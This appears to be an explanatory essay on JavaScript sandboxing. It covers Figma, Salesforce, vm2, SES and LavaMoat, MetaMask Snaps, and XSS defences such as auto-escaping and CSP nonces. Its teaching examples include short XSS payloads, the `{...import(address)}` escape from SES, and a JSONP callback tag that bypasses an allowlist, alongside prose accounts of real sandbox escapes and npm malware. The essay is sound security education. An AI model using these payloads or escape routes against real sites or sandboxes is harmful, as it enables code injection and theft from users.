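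More reports followed in October, and one of the new attacks exploited a September repair. To guard against altered built-ins, Agoric had changed how the shim joined three lists of code-rewriting functions, but the new method let the first list determine what kind of object the join produced. The guest supplied that list, so the guest could drop the shim's safety checks from the result.

Agoric stopped maintaining the shim that month. In *Realms and Evaluator Shim Security*, Warner (2019) reviewed eleven bugs and judged that eight would have been harmless if host and guest had shared one set of frozen built-ins. The host's objects would still have leaked, but the guest could not have used them to reach anything useful. Agoric moved to a design like this, with compartments instead of separate realms.

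### What a separate engine gave Figma

Figma switched to QuickJS, a small JavaScript engine written in C, which it compiled to WebAssembly. In a shared engine, host and guest objects have the same form, so a bug in the sandbox can give the plugin a host object in place of a guest object. QuickJS stores the plugin's objects as bytes in its own block of memory, where a browser object can't exist. If a plugin tries the `log` trick, it gets QuickJS's own `Function`, which can't reach the browser's `window`.

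Figma had the replacement ready in nine days because the membrane let it swap engines without rewriting the programming interface. The change made plugins somewhat slower and the browser's debugger harder to use. *Figma Plugins*, by a developer of mapping plugins, says plugins still run slower than seems right, though it acknowledges that map data is unusually heavy. Agoric had fixed all the known holes in the shim by then, so Figma could have gone back to it, but it preferred to stay with the approach it called "intrinsically more secure".

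An interpreter doesn't provide this protection merely by being an interpreter. SCI runs programs in the language Clojure and can do so on top of JavaScript, and people have used it as a sandbox. But its guests handle ordinary JavaScript values. Borkent, in *SCI sandboxing on JS host considered unsafe*, shows a guest taking a piece of text, asking for its constructor, then asking for the constructor of that, and arriving at the host's `Function`. QuickJS avoids this because the guest's values are in a different format from the host's.

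Figma's boundary depends on WebAssembly working correctly. In October 2026, The Hacker News' *Two Critical Wasmtime Flaws Could Let Malicious WebAssembly Modules Escape Sandboxes* reported compiler bugs in Wasmtime, which runs WebAssembly outside the browser. Browsers have their own WebAssembly compilers, so these bugs don't affect Figma, but a similar bug in a browser's compiler could. Browser makers maintain those compilers, though, and a security flaw in one would endanger every website.

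### Salesforce: a sandbox for each namespace

Salesforce couldn't isolate guest code as completely. A page in its business software may combine components from Salesforce, the customer's developers and other companies that sell through Salesforce's marketplace. These components have to display on the same page and work together, but one company's component shouldn't be able to read another's data.

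Salesforce's first approach, Lightning Locker, resembled Caja's tamed DOM. Locker put secure wrappers around `window`, `document` and page elements, and a component could access only elements it had created. *How Lightning Web Security Compares to Lightning Locker* lists the problems this caused. Libraries failed if they needed functions that the wrappers hid. Components couldn't access the contents of iframes or define new kinds of HTML element, and passing arrays between components could be slow because Locker filtered them.

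The successor, Lightning Web Security, gives each namespace (a name that marks where a component comes from) its own sandbox. The sandbox is a copy of the browser environment with its own global objects, so a library can alter them without affecting other namespaces. Salesforce then changes how individual browser functions behave, and calls these changes distortions. Salesforce's *How Lightning Web Security Works* gives the example of a component in the namespace `c` that sets a cookie named `foo`, which the browser stores as `LSKey-c$foo`. The component can still read the cookie as `foo`, but it can't read cookies from other namespaces.

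Salesforce says the new system is faster because it doesn't use secure wrappers. However, Salesforce's *Understand How LWS Architecture Affects Component Performance* explains that objects passing between a sandbox and the rest of the page still go through Proxies, and that the delay becomes noticeable with tens of thousands of Proxies. Even `Set`, JavaScript's built-in collection type, belongs to the host, so filling one with 100,000 entries is much slower than normal. Salesforce advises developers to copy large data into the sandbox before working on it. Figma had rejected its iframe partly because of that kind of copying, but with Salesforce's system developers can choose which data to copy.

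A distorted function is also harder to debug than a blocked one. In June 2026 Salesforce published a guide by its engineer Tim Dionne about components that work in testing but "silently" return wrong data in production. Browser storage works the same way as cookies, so a component that looks up a value from another namespace gets `null`, as if it had never been stored. If a component changes an object it received from another namespace, the change stays inside its own sandbox. The sender still has the old value, and neither component gets an error. Dionne calls this one of the hardest behaviours to diagnose. An object can also turn into `null` when it passes between namespaces. He recommends converting it to JSON, a plain text format, before sending it, because a string needs no Proxy.

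Only a few functions fail with a visible error, including `document.write`, which can insert scripts that bypass the sandbox, and Workers, which run scripts in the background outside it. Salesforce suggests considering an iframe for a component that needs Workers.

These silent failures come from the same choice that made old libraries work again. Locker gave components an obviously reduced browser, and code that needed the missing parts broke. Lightning Web Security imitates a complete browser, so the code runs, but some of what it accesses is a private copy.

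The sandboxes also provide less protection than the weather widget's host would want. Components in the same namespace share a sandbox, so they have no such protection from each other. Network requests mostly work as normal, subject to the browser's rules and any restrictions the customer has configured. The system therefore keeps a component away from other people's data but does little to control where it sends the data it is allowed to read.

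Salesforce has also sought support for sandboxing in the engine itself. *Introducing ShadowRealm* (Balter, 2022) describes a proposed JavaScript feature that would let a page create a new realm directly. Only simple values such as text and numbers could cross the boundary, along with functions that the engine wraps automatically. The passed-in `log` function would then be safe without special care. Salesforce would still need its own membrane because its components exchange objects.

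### vm2

Node.js runs JavaScript outside the browser, usually on servers, where a guest that escapes may gain access to the server's files. Node's `vm` module gives code a separate global object, but a guest can leave it by following constructors, just as with `log`. The library vm2 adds Proxies to block such routes. By July 2023, more than 200,000 projects on GitHub used vm2, according to *The indomitable maintainer spirit versus the indifferent cruelty of JavaScript* (Vonblankenburg, 2023). It had also had eight security advisories in a year, almost all for escapes.

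That month its creator, Patrik Simek, discontinued the project. Simek wrote that the team faced an escape "so complicated that fixing it seems impossible". The notice gave special thanks to XmiliaH, who had broken the Realms shim and spent four years maintaining vm2. XmiliaH concluded that Node itself intercepted some of the guest's calls, so objects got through without a Proxy around them. The team couldn't fix this in its own code because the fault was in the module vm2 was built on.

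The project nevertheless came back in late 2025, according to The CyberSec Guru's *Security Alert*. In January 2026, the security company Semgrep told users to upgrade immediately because of a new critical escape (*New Sandbox Escape Affecting Popular nodejs Sandbox library vm2*, 2026). In May, the developers fixed four more flaws in a single release, all with the highest possible severity score, according to heise's *Node.js*. OffSeq's *Threat Radar* (2026) describes a simpler flaw from September. In some configurations, vm2 checked only the beginning of a module's path against its list of permitted modules. A guest with permission to load one module could therefore also load a neighbouring module whose name started the same way, which ran with the host's full privileges.

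The developers of vm2 still maintain it but no longer present it as sufficient. In the documentation, they warn that people will probably find new escapes, and they urge stronger isolation for code from complete strangers. They consider vm2 suitable when the guest code needs close contact with the host's objects and comes from a fairly trusted source, such as a plugin author the company has vetted.

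### Spectre and secrets in shared memory

In all of these escapes, the guest got hold of an object that the host hadn't meant to share. Spectre, a family of attacks that researchers disclosed in January 2018, doesn't require such an object. It exploits the way processors save time by guessing what a program will do next.

Suppose the guest's code reads an entry from a list, after checking that the entry's number isn't past the end. The guest runs this code many times with valid numbers, until the processor predicts that the check will succeed. Then the guest supplies a number far past the end. Before the check is complete, the processor fetches a byte that belongs to the host, perhaps part of a password. The guest's next instruction uses that byte to choose which entry of a second list to load. When the check fails, the processor discards this work, but the loaded entry stays in its cache,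 a small, fast memory. The guest then measures how long each entry of the second list takes to read, and the fastest one reveals the byte.

*Spectre Is Here to Stay* (2019), by McIlroy, Sevcik and colleagues on Google's V8 JavaScript engine, concluded that untrusted code could read all the memory in its process this way, and that no known software fix was complete. Making the browser's clocks less precise didn't solve the problem, because untrusted code can repeat the operation until even a coarse clock shows the difference in timing. Chrome's main defence was to run different websites in different processes, which keeps one site's secrets out of memory that another site's code can reach.

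The Realms shim, Lightning Web Security and vm2 all keep guest and host in one process. Spectre can read memory but not change it, so these sandboxes can try to stop a guest from changing the host's data, but they can't guarantee that the data stays secret. A guest that reads a login token may be able to use it to make changes too, and the risk is greater if the guest can use the network, as a Salesforce component usually can. Figma's QuickJS probably makes a Spectre attack much harder, because the plugin has little control over the exact machine instructions that run. However, the plugin's memory is still in the same process as the editor's.

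A guest can therefore have its own engine or heap and still share a process with the host. Both Simek and the current vm2 documentation suggest isolated-vm, which gives each guest a separate heap within V8, much as Cloudflare does for its customers' programs. The documentation lists it among tools with "true process or hardware-level isolation", but the separate heaps can be in one process. Even an iframe protects against Spectre only if the browser puts it in another process, which web standards allow but don't require.

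### Rich access or a strong boundary

Warner's account of the Realms shim explains why these sandboxes had so much trouble with objects. If the host's built-ins are unfrozen and powerful, any object that crosses the boundary can lead back to them, so only simple values such as strings and numbers are safe to pass directly. Figma's membrane copies such values, and Dionne's advice to send JSON has the same effect. To share live objects, a host has to wrap each one correctly, along with everything a guest can reach from it.

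The drawbacks of a strong boundary depend on how much of the host's data the guest handles. The weather widget would lose almost nothing in an iframe, but a Figma plugin may go through thousands of shapes, which made the iframe unusable. As a compromise, Figma used QuickJS, which keeps the plugin's objects apart from the editor's but runs on the same thread, so the plugin can read a shape's width immediately. The main drawback was slower plugin code, and Figma also could not run the plugin's main code in a separate process.

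None of these boundaries limits what the guest does with the access it was meant to have. A plugin with permission to edit the document can ruin it from inside QuickJS, and one that can also use the network can send the document to a stranger. Figma controls network access separately. Kolibri Sync's *3.2.1 Figma Plugin* explains that each plugin comes with a file listing the internet domains it may contact.

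## Hardened JavaScript (SES): what changed after Caja and who adopted it

After abandoning the Realms shim in 2019, Agoric still wanted to run guest code in the host's own JavaScript engine, but with host and guest sharing one frozen set of built-in objects.

The result is Hardened JavaScript, also called SES (Secure ECMAScript). ECMAScript is the official name of the JavaScript standard. Programmers can add SES to most browsers and to Node.js with the `ses` library. The library is part of Endo, an open-source project that LavaMoat's glossary describes as a distributed sandbox for JavaScript. *SES*, the library's documentation on npm, states that SES starts where Caja left off.

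### What the language took over from Caja

Caja had to rewrite a guest's code because the JavaScript of 1999 gave a host almost no way to enforce rules while the guest ran. The 2009 and 2015 editions of the standard supplied most of what Caja had been adding through rewriting.

The 2009 edition introduced strict mode, an opt-in version of the language with tighter rules. In strict code, a function called on its own gets `undefined` for `this` instead of the global object, so a host no longer needs Caja's rules for functions that use `this`. The same edition added `Object.freeze`, which makes the engine block any change to an object's properties, replacing Caja's checks on writes.

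In 2015, JavaScript added weak maps, which are tables that attach a record to an object without storing anything on the object. Code without access to the table can't find the record, so a host that uses a weak map doesn't need Caja's reserved names.

The same edition added Proxies. The Realms shim had shown that a host can combine a Proxy with the old `with` statement to control what a guest's free variables refer to. The engine can then run the guest's program almost unchanged. The `ses` library still translates modules, the separate files that make up a larger program, because it has to link them itself.

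### The weather widget in a compartment

With SES, the webmail company could load its weather widget like this:

```
import 'ses';
lockdown();

const widget = new Compartment({
  globals: harden({ forecastBox, getForecast }),
  __options__: true,
});
widget.evaluate(widgetCode);
```

The host calls `lockdown()` once, before any guest code runs. This freezes the built-in objects that all programs share, as Caja had done, and restricts a few built-ins that reveal too much. For example, in browsers built on Google's V8 engine, an error normally lists the functions that were running, and the list can include file names from the host's disk. Lockdown hides this list from guests.

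The host keeps all its powers after lockdown, so its own code can still use `window` and `fetch`. The compartment gives the widget a different global object, which holds only the standard built-ins and the two things the host put there, so the widget can't find `document`. The `__options__` line is a temporary compatibility marker.

Lockdown also closes the route that made a simple `log` function dangerous under the Realms shim, by replacing the function's constructor with a dummy that throws an error. Each compartment has its own working `Function` and `eval`, and any code they create runs with that compartment's globals. The host can therefore harden `log` and hand it over without first writing a membrane.

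Sharing the built-ins also has a practical advantage. An array from one realm fails another realm's `instanceof Array` test, which breaks some libraries. Compartments share the same `Array` constructor, so the test works between them.

Unlike Caja, SES also withholds the clock and random numbers: in a new compartment, `Date.now()` and `Math.random()` don't work unless the host supplies them.

### Frozen objects that still change

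The third function, `harden`, freezes an object together with everything reachable from it through properties and inheritance. Suppose the host gives two guests the same small object, adapted here from the documentation:

```
let counter = 0;
const tally = harden({
  inc() { return counter++; },
});
```

Neither guest can replace `inc` with its own function to spy on the other. But the first call returns 0 and the second returns 1, because `inc` can still change the variable `counter`. Hardening protects the object's properties but not the state that its functions use. The two guests could communicate through `tally`, since each can tell from the number how often the other has called `inc`. Similarly, GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Ses package* notes that anybody who holds a hardened `Map`, JavaScript's built-in lookup table, can read and write its contents.

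The same behaviour is useful for narrowing a power. Suppose the host has an object for a file of meeting notes, with functions to read, write and delete it, and wants a guest to be able to read the notes and do nothing else:

```
function readOnly(file) {
  return harden({
    read: () => file.read(),
  });
}
const notes = readOnly(meetingNotes);
```

The host puts `notes` in the guest's compartment and keeps `meetingNotes`. The guest can call `notes.read()`, but `notes.write` doesn't exist. The variable `file` still refers to the full file object, but JavaScript doesn't let outside code access the variables inside a function. If the host gives `notes` to several guests, `harden` stops any of them from replacing `read` with a function that returns false text to the others.

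The wrapper limits what the guest can do to the file, but the host can still change the notes, and the guest will read the new version. A guest that also has a network function can send the text anywhere. The host also has to consider what `read` returns. Node.js programs often receive a file's contents as a Buffer, a block of raw bytes. LavaMoat's *Reviewing Policy* warns that Node keeps buffers in a shared pool of memory and that each buffer exposes the whole pool. A guest with "read-only" access to a file could then see other data the program was handling, perhaps a password. The host can avoid this by returning plain text.

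### What SES leaves to the host

SES has no counterpart to Caja's tamed DOM. A compartment starts without `document` or page elements, so the host must write `forecastBox` as a small object with, say, one function that sets plain text. If the host passed in the real page element, the widget could still use it to reach the rest of the page. By leaving out the DOM, SES's developers avoided the part of Caja that was probably the slowest and hardest to maintain, but they also gave up Caja's original purpose of running other people's gadgets with little change.

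A guest can also freeze the whole application by going into an endless loop, because it runs on the same thread as the host. It can use up memory too. Hardened JavaScript, the project's website, therefore recommends combining compartments with separate processes or workers.

SES defends against Spectre by withholding the clock that the attack relies on, but many useful programs need timers. If a host supplies timers, the developers advise running only one party's code in that process and keeping confidential data out of it, so that the process boundary protects the data.

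### Who uses it

The project's website lists three companies that use SES. Agoric uses it to confine smart contracts, which are programs that hold and move assets on a blockchain. Moddable uses it on embedded devices, such as the small computers inside appliances. MetaMask, which makes a cryptocurrency wallet that runs as a browser extension, uses it for plugins called Snaps and, through its tool LavaMoat, for the third-party packages the wallet is built from.

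Few public figures on use are available. The security company Socket recorded 21,721 weekly downloads of LavaMoat's plugin for webpack, a tool that combines a program's files for the browser (*@lavamoat/webpack*), and 22,983 of the package that runs Snaps (*@metamask/snaps-execution-environments*). Neither figure is a count of people, because automated build systems can account for many downloads and one download may end up in a wallet with many users. Downloads also don't show whether the software stops attacks, which depends partly on how carefully developers use it.

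### How LavaMoat decides what a package may do

JavaScript programmers get most of their outside code from npm, a public registry of more than two million packages. A package usually depends on others, which depend on still others. *NodeShield* (Cornelissen and Balliu, 2025) cites research that a package relies on average on 79 others, from 40 maintainers. All of this code normally has the same powers as the application that includes it. In one kind of software supply-chain attack, somebody takes over a maintainer's account and publishes a malicious version of a package, which then runs in applications that install the update.

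LavaMoat gives each package its own compartment. Writing the list of permissions for hundreds of packages by hand would be a huge job, so LavaMoat generates it. It scans the source code of every package and notes which global variables, built-in modules and other packages the code refers to. It then writes these to a policy file. The entry for chalk, a package that colours text in a terminal, looks like this in an example by the security firm OtterSec:

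```
"chalk": {
  "globals": {
    "navigator.userAgent": true,
    "navigator.userAgentData": true
  }
}
```

When the application runs, LavaMoat first calls `lockdown()`, then creates chalk's compartment with only those two properties of `navigator`, which identify the browser. If chalk tries to import another package, LavaMoat's own import function blocks it because chalk's entry lists none. LavaMoat's *Using Policies* explains that a policy can grant access to a single property of a powerful object, such as `fs.readFile` without the rest of `fs`, Node's file module. It also explains that LavaMoat identifies a package by its path through the dependency tree so that an attacker can't get a trusted package's permissions by publishing another package under the same name. The policy doesn't restrict the application's own code.

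A generated policy records what a package uses, which may be more than it needs. For example, a package may need only one setting from `process.env`, but LavaMoat's scan may not detect this and may grant all of `process`. In Node.js, code with access to that object can start other programs on the machine. A developer can narrow the grant in a second file, `policy-override.json`, which takes precedence.

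The scan also can't distinguish legitimate needs from malicious ones, so if a developer generates the policy while a malicious version of a package is installed, LavaMoat will grant whatever powers it sees the malicious code using. LavaMoat's guide therefore warns that the first policy "doesn't provide security on its own". The protection comes from a person who reads the policy file, reviews the changes to it after each update, and questions unexpected powers, such as network access for a package that formats text.

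In a large project this happens constantly. The MetaMask contributor itsyoboieltr (2026) described a change to the bot that updates the wallet's policies. The bot would copy the required changes from the log of a failed check instead of regenerating everything, which would cut the time from minutes to seconds. Even with a faster bot, someone still has to judge whether the package should have the new power.

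### What a permitted package can still do

A package that has dangerous permissions can abuse them without breaking any rule. One with `fetch` can send out any data the application gives it, and one with `document` can create an iframe and take a fresh, unrestricted set of globals from it. Even `addEventListener`, which lets code react to clicks and keystrokes, is risky, because the browser passes the listener an event object through which it can reach the page.

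Permissions can also spread from one package to another. A package with no network access may be able to send data through an imported package that has it, which makes the imported package a confused deputy. To address this, Cornelissen and Balliu's own system, NodeShield, shows the reviewer each package's powers together with those of everything it depends on, but enforces only the smaller set that the package uses directly. Reviewers using LavaMoat are told to trace for themselves how packages are connected.

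Some attacks need no permission. If a wallet uses a package to format a payment address, a malicious version of the package could return the attacker's address instead.

### LavaMoat and the npm attacks

On 8 September 2025, attackers published malicious versions of 18 popular npm packages, including chalk. Palo Alto Networks' *Widespread npm Supply Chain Attack Puts Billions of Weekly Downloads at Risk* (2025) put their combined downloads at more than 2.6 billion a week. According to OtterSec's *How to Survive Supply-Chain Attacks* (2025), the malicious code looked for a cryptocurrency wallet in the user's browser. It replaced the page's `fetch` function with one that swapped payment addresses in incoming data for the attackers' own, and it changed the recipient in transactions the user was about to sign. It replaced each address with the most similar-looking one the attackers had, so that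 the change was easy to miss.

OtterSec ran the malicious version of chalk under a policy that LavaMoat had generated from the previous, clean version. The attack failed when the code tried to redefine `fetch`, because lockdown had made the global object unchangeable. It would have failed later anyway, since chalk's two permissions include neither network access nor access to the wallet. This is good evidence that LavaMoat works as designed against a real attack, although OtterSec tested only one package and has also audited the tool. In the real attack, the attacker had stolen only about $1,000 after two days.

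The best evidence from a larger test comes from NodeShield, which also limits each package separately but isn't built on SES. It sorts powers into only seven groups, such as files, network and running commands. Cornelissen and Balliu tested it on 67 npm malware samples from 46 packages and found that it could stop 66. Most of these packages had been malicious from their first version. A policy generated from such a package would often grant the powers needed for the attack, so the result depends on a developer reviewing the policy and refusing those powers.

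A trusted package that turns malicious in an update is the harder case for a reviewer. The test included four such packages that attacked while the application ran, and NodeShield stopped three. It missed node-ipc, a package for communication between programs, because the benign version already used files and the network, and the malicious code needed no other access. LavaMoat can grant `readFile` without `writeFile`, but that would help only if the benign version needed less access than the attack.

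One of the attacks that NodeShield stopped was the 2018 theft from users of Copay, another cryptocurrency wallet. The attackers added a new package, flatmap-stream, to a tool that Copay's developers used to build the wallet. During the build, flatmap-stream altered another package so that the finished wallet leaked its users' private keys. The attackers had scrambled the code, so NodeShield's scan didn't detect that it used files, the network and encryption. NodeShield therefore granted it none of these powers and blocked it when it tried to use them. If the code hadn't been scrambled, the new powers would have appeared in the policy, where a reviewer could have noticed them.

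Most npm malware attacks during installation, before the application runs. Packages can include scripts that run as soon as a developer installs them, and 1,594 of the 1,635 labelled packages that Cornelissen and Balliu had collected attacked this way. Compartments in the finished application can't stop these attacks. LavaMoat has a separate tool, allow-scripts, that turns off installation scripts except for those on a list, and its developers recommend this as the first step. The tool relies on the package manager, the program that downloads and installs packages, to apply the setting correctly. The security company Koi found six flaws in four package managers, including ways to bypass script blocking. The developers of three package managers fixed their flaws, but npm's developers closed the report and called the behaviour expected.

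The Shai-Hulud worm of September 2025 spread through installation scripts. According to Phoenix Security, it searched the developer's machine for passwords and access tokens, then used them to publish infected versions of the developer's packages. Socket reported a similar worm in February 2026 that also tampered with developers' AI tools. For attacks like these, allow-scripts is the relevant part of LavaMoat, and SES matters only if the malicious code gets past it.

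OSV's *MAL-2026-13099* (2026) describes a malicious package from August 2026 that posed as a webpack plugin and downloaded and ran a program as soon as a developer's build loaded it. LavaMoat's webpack tool restricts the code that webpack bundles, but according to its documentation, other webpack plugins can intentionally bypass it. To restrict such a plugin, developers would have to run the build itself under LavaMoat's Node.js version. The plugin would then need permission to use the network and start programs, which a careful reviewer would probably refuse.

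### The cost in speed

NodeShield added less than a millisecond to each server request, but it cut throughput by up to 12% and raised memory use by 43% to 251%. Short programs took up to about five times as long to run, because NodeShield does most of its work at startup. These figures are only a rough guide to LavaMoat's overhead, because NodeShield creates a new engine context for each file, whereas LavaMoat uses compartments that share their built-ins.

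In a benchmark of WebAssembly code inside a Snap, most operations took about 3.25 times as long as they did natively. The likely cause was how SES freezes typed arrays, JavaScript's compact lists of numbers, which WebAssembly code uses heavily. An ordinary Snap that fetches a price and displays it should slow down much less.

Freezing the built-ins also breaks some older packages. For example, objects inherit a `toString` function, and programs often give an object its own version with a simple assignment. That assignment fails if the inherited function is frozen, so the package's author has to use a longer form.

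### Audits and holes

Three engineers from an outside firm reviewed SES for four weeks in June 2021 and found no new vulnerabilities. MetaMask and Agoric held a joint bug hunt the next month and found no critical flaws.

In August 2023, however, the developers disclosed a hole that OSV's *CVE-2023-39532* (2023) rates 9.8 out of 10. SES has to keep guests from using the `import` expression, which loads and runs more code and which had broken Caja in 2017. A guest could get around this by writing the expression after three dots, JavaScript's notation for copying an object's contents:

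`{...import(address)}`

The guest needed no permissions to do this. In Node.js, it could run any code. In a browser, the damage depended on the page's Content-Security-Policy, which lists the sources from which the page may load scripts. A strict policy would have blocked most of the attack even though SES had failed.

The next serious flaw, reported in OSV's *CVE-2025-32792* (2025), made some of a page's own variables visible inside compartments. JavaScript stores variables declared with `let`, `const` or `class` separately from the global object, so giving the guest a new global object didn't hide them. Any guest could have read a secret key that the page kept in such a variable. Version 1.12.0 fixed this.

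These holes are fewer than vm2's, but like Caja's, they arose because the language had a feature the sandbox didn't fully cover. The SES developers openly say that their guarantees assume a JavaScript engine without any new syntax that gives a guest access to a mutable object.

OtterSec's *Supply Chain Attacks* (2024) describes two flaws in LavaMoat. The first arose because LavaMoat removed certain comments from a package after checking its syntax. A package could arrange its code so that the removal left part of it outside the sandbox. The second flaw let a package create an iframe that MetaMask's protective code didn't detect, and use it to recover powers that LavaMoat had deleted from the page. An attacker who controlled one of MetaMask's packages could have combined the two to take the user's encrypted keys from the wallet's storage. The developers fixed the first flaw in under two days.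 For the second, MetaMask proposed that browsers add a feature to let a page control the iframes created inside it.

OtterSec also audited the webpack plugin in late 2024 and found further bypasses. LavaMoat still labels the plugin an open beta in its documentation and tells developers to use it at their own risk.

### Snaps: a sandbox inside an iframe

A Snap is a plugin for the MetaMask wallet that anyone can write, for example to add support for another blockchain. The open beta began on 12 September 2023, according to the security company Least Authority. MetaMask can't review everything each Snap does, and the keys to a user's money are in the same wallet, so it uses several boundaries at once, which Halltari and Obici describe in *MetaMask Snaps*. A Snap runs in a compartment inside a sandboxed iframe, and LavaMoat restricts the iframe's supporting packages. If a Snap escaped the compartment,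 it would still be in the iframe, which can reach the wallet only by sending messages.

Each Snap comes with a list of the permissions it requests, which MetaMask shows to the user. The wallet turns the approved permissions into objects and puts them in the Snap's compartment. A Snap has the `fetch` function only if the user approved network access. This is close to what Caja's designers intended for gadgets, with the user deciding which references to hand over.

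Halltari and Obici found a flaw in one of these objects. A Snap makes requests to the wallet through a function, `snap.request`. The function checked that the request was of a permitted kind, then converted it to JSON and forwarded the result. But a JavaScript object can have a method that controls how it is converted to JSON. Their Snap passed a request to show a dialog box, which was allowed, and conversion turned it into a request to send money. The wallet would then ask the user to approve a transaction that the Snap had no right to propose. MetaMask fixed the flaw by converting the request first and checking the result. The same kind of trick had worked against ADsafe more than a decade earlier. SES and the iframe both worked correctly, but the mistake was in the host's own code, which neither checks.

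The Starknet Snap had a fault on the other side of the boundary. This Snap can sign transactions on the Starknet blockchain, and it normally asks the user first. Vulners' *Authorization Bypass in Starknet Snap via enableAuthorize parameter* reports that a website could control whether the Snap asked, so any site could get it to sign without the user's approval. The Snap was a confused deputy, and confinement could not prevent this because the Snap was allowed to sign transactions.

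Since SES can't interrupt an infinite loop, MetaMask stops a Snap that runs too long. In an audit of one Snap, the security company Hacken found that Snaps could evade this time limit.

### Compartments and the language standard

Unlike strict mode, freezing, proxies and weak maps, `Compartment` is not part of standard JavaScript. Engineers from Agoric, Moddable and Salesforce, whose own sandbox derives from the same work, have proposed it to TC39, the committee that maintains the language. According to Farias's *Compartments*, the proposal reached Stage 1 in April 2020. Stage 1 means that the committee considered the problem worth studying, and features enter the language after Stage 4.

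In June 2022, Kowal (2022), in *TC39 Compartments on Matrix*, saw "a sudden upwelling of political will" for the proposal and hoped to get it ready for Stage 2 by the next meeting. TC39's *ECMAScript proposals* explains that the committee expects a Stage 2 feature to enter the language eventually. But the proposal was still at Stage 1 in November 2025, and nobody had changed its text since December 2022.

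Moddable has built compartments into XS, its own JavaScript engine. Everyone else has to imitate them with the `ses` library, whose developers have to keep up with each new language feature. If browsers supported compartments directly, browser makers would have to make sure that new features didn't break them.

### Why wallets adopted it

A developer who adopts LavaMoat has to replace or repair packages that break, and review the policy after every update. Cornelissen and Balliu estimated the work of reviewing updates from the history of six server projects. Updates to existing packages rarely required new powers. Changes that also added new packages took more work, and in the worst project each one required reviewing almost 13 powers on average. LavaMoat's policies probably take longer to read than the ones in this study because they list individual functions.

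Most website developers have little reason to do this work. Wallet developers have more, because a thief who gets the keys can take the money at once, and the owner usually can't get it back. The Copay attack and the September 2025 malware both targeted cryptocurrency. A smart contract on Agoric's blockchain may also hold other people's assets, so the same reasoning applies.

Agoric also decides which functions a contract can call, and MetaMask decides which requests a Snap can make. So neither has to build a convincing copy of the DOM and update it whenever a browser changes, as Google had to with Caja. A smart contract loses little when SES removes the clock and random numbers, because every computer on the blockchain must get the same result from running it. The packages inside MetaMask's own user interface do need the DOM, and one of OtterSec's two bypasses went through it.

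This explanation rests on only three companies, and personal connections may account for some of the pattern. Agoric employed Miller and Kowal, who developed SES, and its engineers worked closely with MetaMask's. Moddable fits only half of the explanation. A household appliance's manufacturer can decide exactly which functions a guest program gets, but there is rarely any money to steal from the appliance.

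## Trusted Types and auto-escaping: tracking where web text came from

A host that uses SES or Caja knows which code is the guest's and decides to run it. But a stranger can also get code into a page by typing it where the developer expected ordinary text, such as a name or a search term. Browser makers and large websites therefore built another defence, which tries to stop untrusted text from becoming code rather than confining code.

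### How text becomes code

Suppose the webmail page has a search box. When the user searches for "invoice", the browser puts the word in the page's address, and a script displays it above the results:

```
const term = new URLSearchParams(location.search).get("q");
heading.innerHTML = term;
```

Assigning a string to `innerHTML` makes the browser read it as HTML. That does no harm with "invoice", but an attacker can send the user a link to the same page with a different search term:

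`<img src="x" onerror="deleteInbox()">`

The browser fails to load an image from the address "x", so it runs the code in `onerror`. This is cross-site scripting (XSS), in which the browser parses a stranger's text as part of a trusted page's code and runs it with all the page's privileges. In *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, Wang, Bangert and Kern use a similar search page to explain how Google's engineers tried to eliminate such bugs.

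This example is DOM-based XSS because the page's own script mixes the stranger's text into the HTML in the user's browser. In server-side XSS, the server does this before sending the page.

The bug is easy to fix once it's found. The developer can use `textContent`, which displays a string without reading it as HTML. But *Securing the Tangled Web*, an article on preventing these bugs through software design, calls them "deceptively simple in cause and remedy" and still surprisingly hard to prevent in large projects. One reason is that text may pass through several servers and databases before a script displays it, and the programmer writing that script sees only a string, with no record of where it came from.

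### Escaping each value for its position

Servers usually build pages from templates, which are HTML files with gaps for values. This one might display a message in the webmail page:

```
<p>Message from {name}</p>
<a href="{site}">Sender's website</a>
<script>prepareReply({name});</script>
```

The template system treats everything outside the braces as trusted, because the developer wrote it, and the values inserted at the braces as untrusted. With contextual auto-escaping, the system works out where in the HTML each value will appear and converts it so that it can't break out of that position.

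If the sender's name is `<script>steal()</script>`, the system replaces each `<` in the paragraph with `&lt;`, the HTML code for displaying that character. The user sees an odd name, and no script runs. HTML escaping isn't enough for the link, because it would leave an address such as `javascript:steal()` unchanged, and clicking the link would run the code. The system therefore also checks the type of address and replaces a dangerous one with something harmless. In the third line, it turns the name into a quoted JavaScript string and escapes any characters that could end the string or the script.

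The same name must be escaped differently in a paragraph than in a script, so a website can't make text safe for every use when it arrives. Google also requires strict templates, which don't let developers turn off escaping. The popular web framework Django is more lenient. It escapes values automatically but lets developers exempt a string with the function `mark_safe`.

### Lists of allowed sites

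Content Security Policy (CSP) is meant to limit the damage when a stranger's HTML gets into a page anyway. The server sends the browser a policy with the page, traditionally a list of sites the page may load scripts from. By default, such a policy also blocks code written directly in the HTML, including the `onerror` code in the search example.

In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues collected 26,011 different Content Security Policies from pages in a Google search index. They judged that an attacker could easily bypass 94.72% of them.

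Of the 22,425 policies that tried to restrict scripts, 87.63% gave almost no protection, whatever sites they listed, because they contained a setting that allowed code in the HTML. Many websites had a lot of such code and would have had to rewrite it to remove the setting. The lists were also a problem, since 79.17% of the same policies trusted at least one site that an attacker could exploit. Weichselbaum and colleagues then looked at the 2,437 stricter policies that had no obvious mistakes, such as allowing code in the HTML. They could still bypass 51.05% of them, mostly because a site on the list hosted something an attacker could use.

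For example, some servers return data wrapped in a call to a function, and let whoever requests the data choose the function's name. If the webmail company's policy allows scripts from such a server, an attacker can inject this tag:

`<script src="https://maps.example/data?callback=deleteInbox"></script>`

The browser runs the response because it comes from an allowed site, and the response begins by calling `deleteInbox`. The map server has become a confused deputy, because the attacker has used its place on the list to run a command of their choice. The server's owner may never have heard of the webmail company's policy, and without that policy the feature would pose no particular danger to the webmail page.

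Of the 15 sites that appeared most often on the lists, 14 hosted something similar, although two of them were exploitable only if the policy also allowed `eval`. A typical list had 12 entries, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies whose lists were that length.

They recommended using nonces instead. A nonce is a random value that the server creates afresh for each response. The server puts it in the policy and on every script tag that it intends to run:

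`<script nonce="k7Qz2p" src="/mail.js"></script>`

An attacker who injects a script tag can't guess the nonce, so the browser ignores the tag even if it points to a site the company trusts. Scripts often load other scripts, which wouldn't have the nonce, so Weichselbaum and colleagues proposed the `strict-dynamic` setting, which lets a trusted script pass its permission on to scripts it adds.

Google Maps Activities, a service with four million monthly users, started with a list of addresses in February 2015. The list needed five major changes that year and grew to 15 long addresses, at least one of which an attacker could have exploited. After the team switched to nonces, it did not need to change the policy again before the paper appeared.

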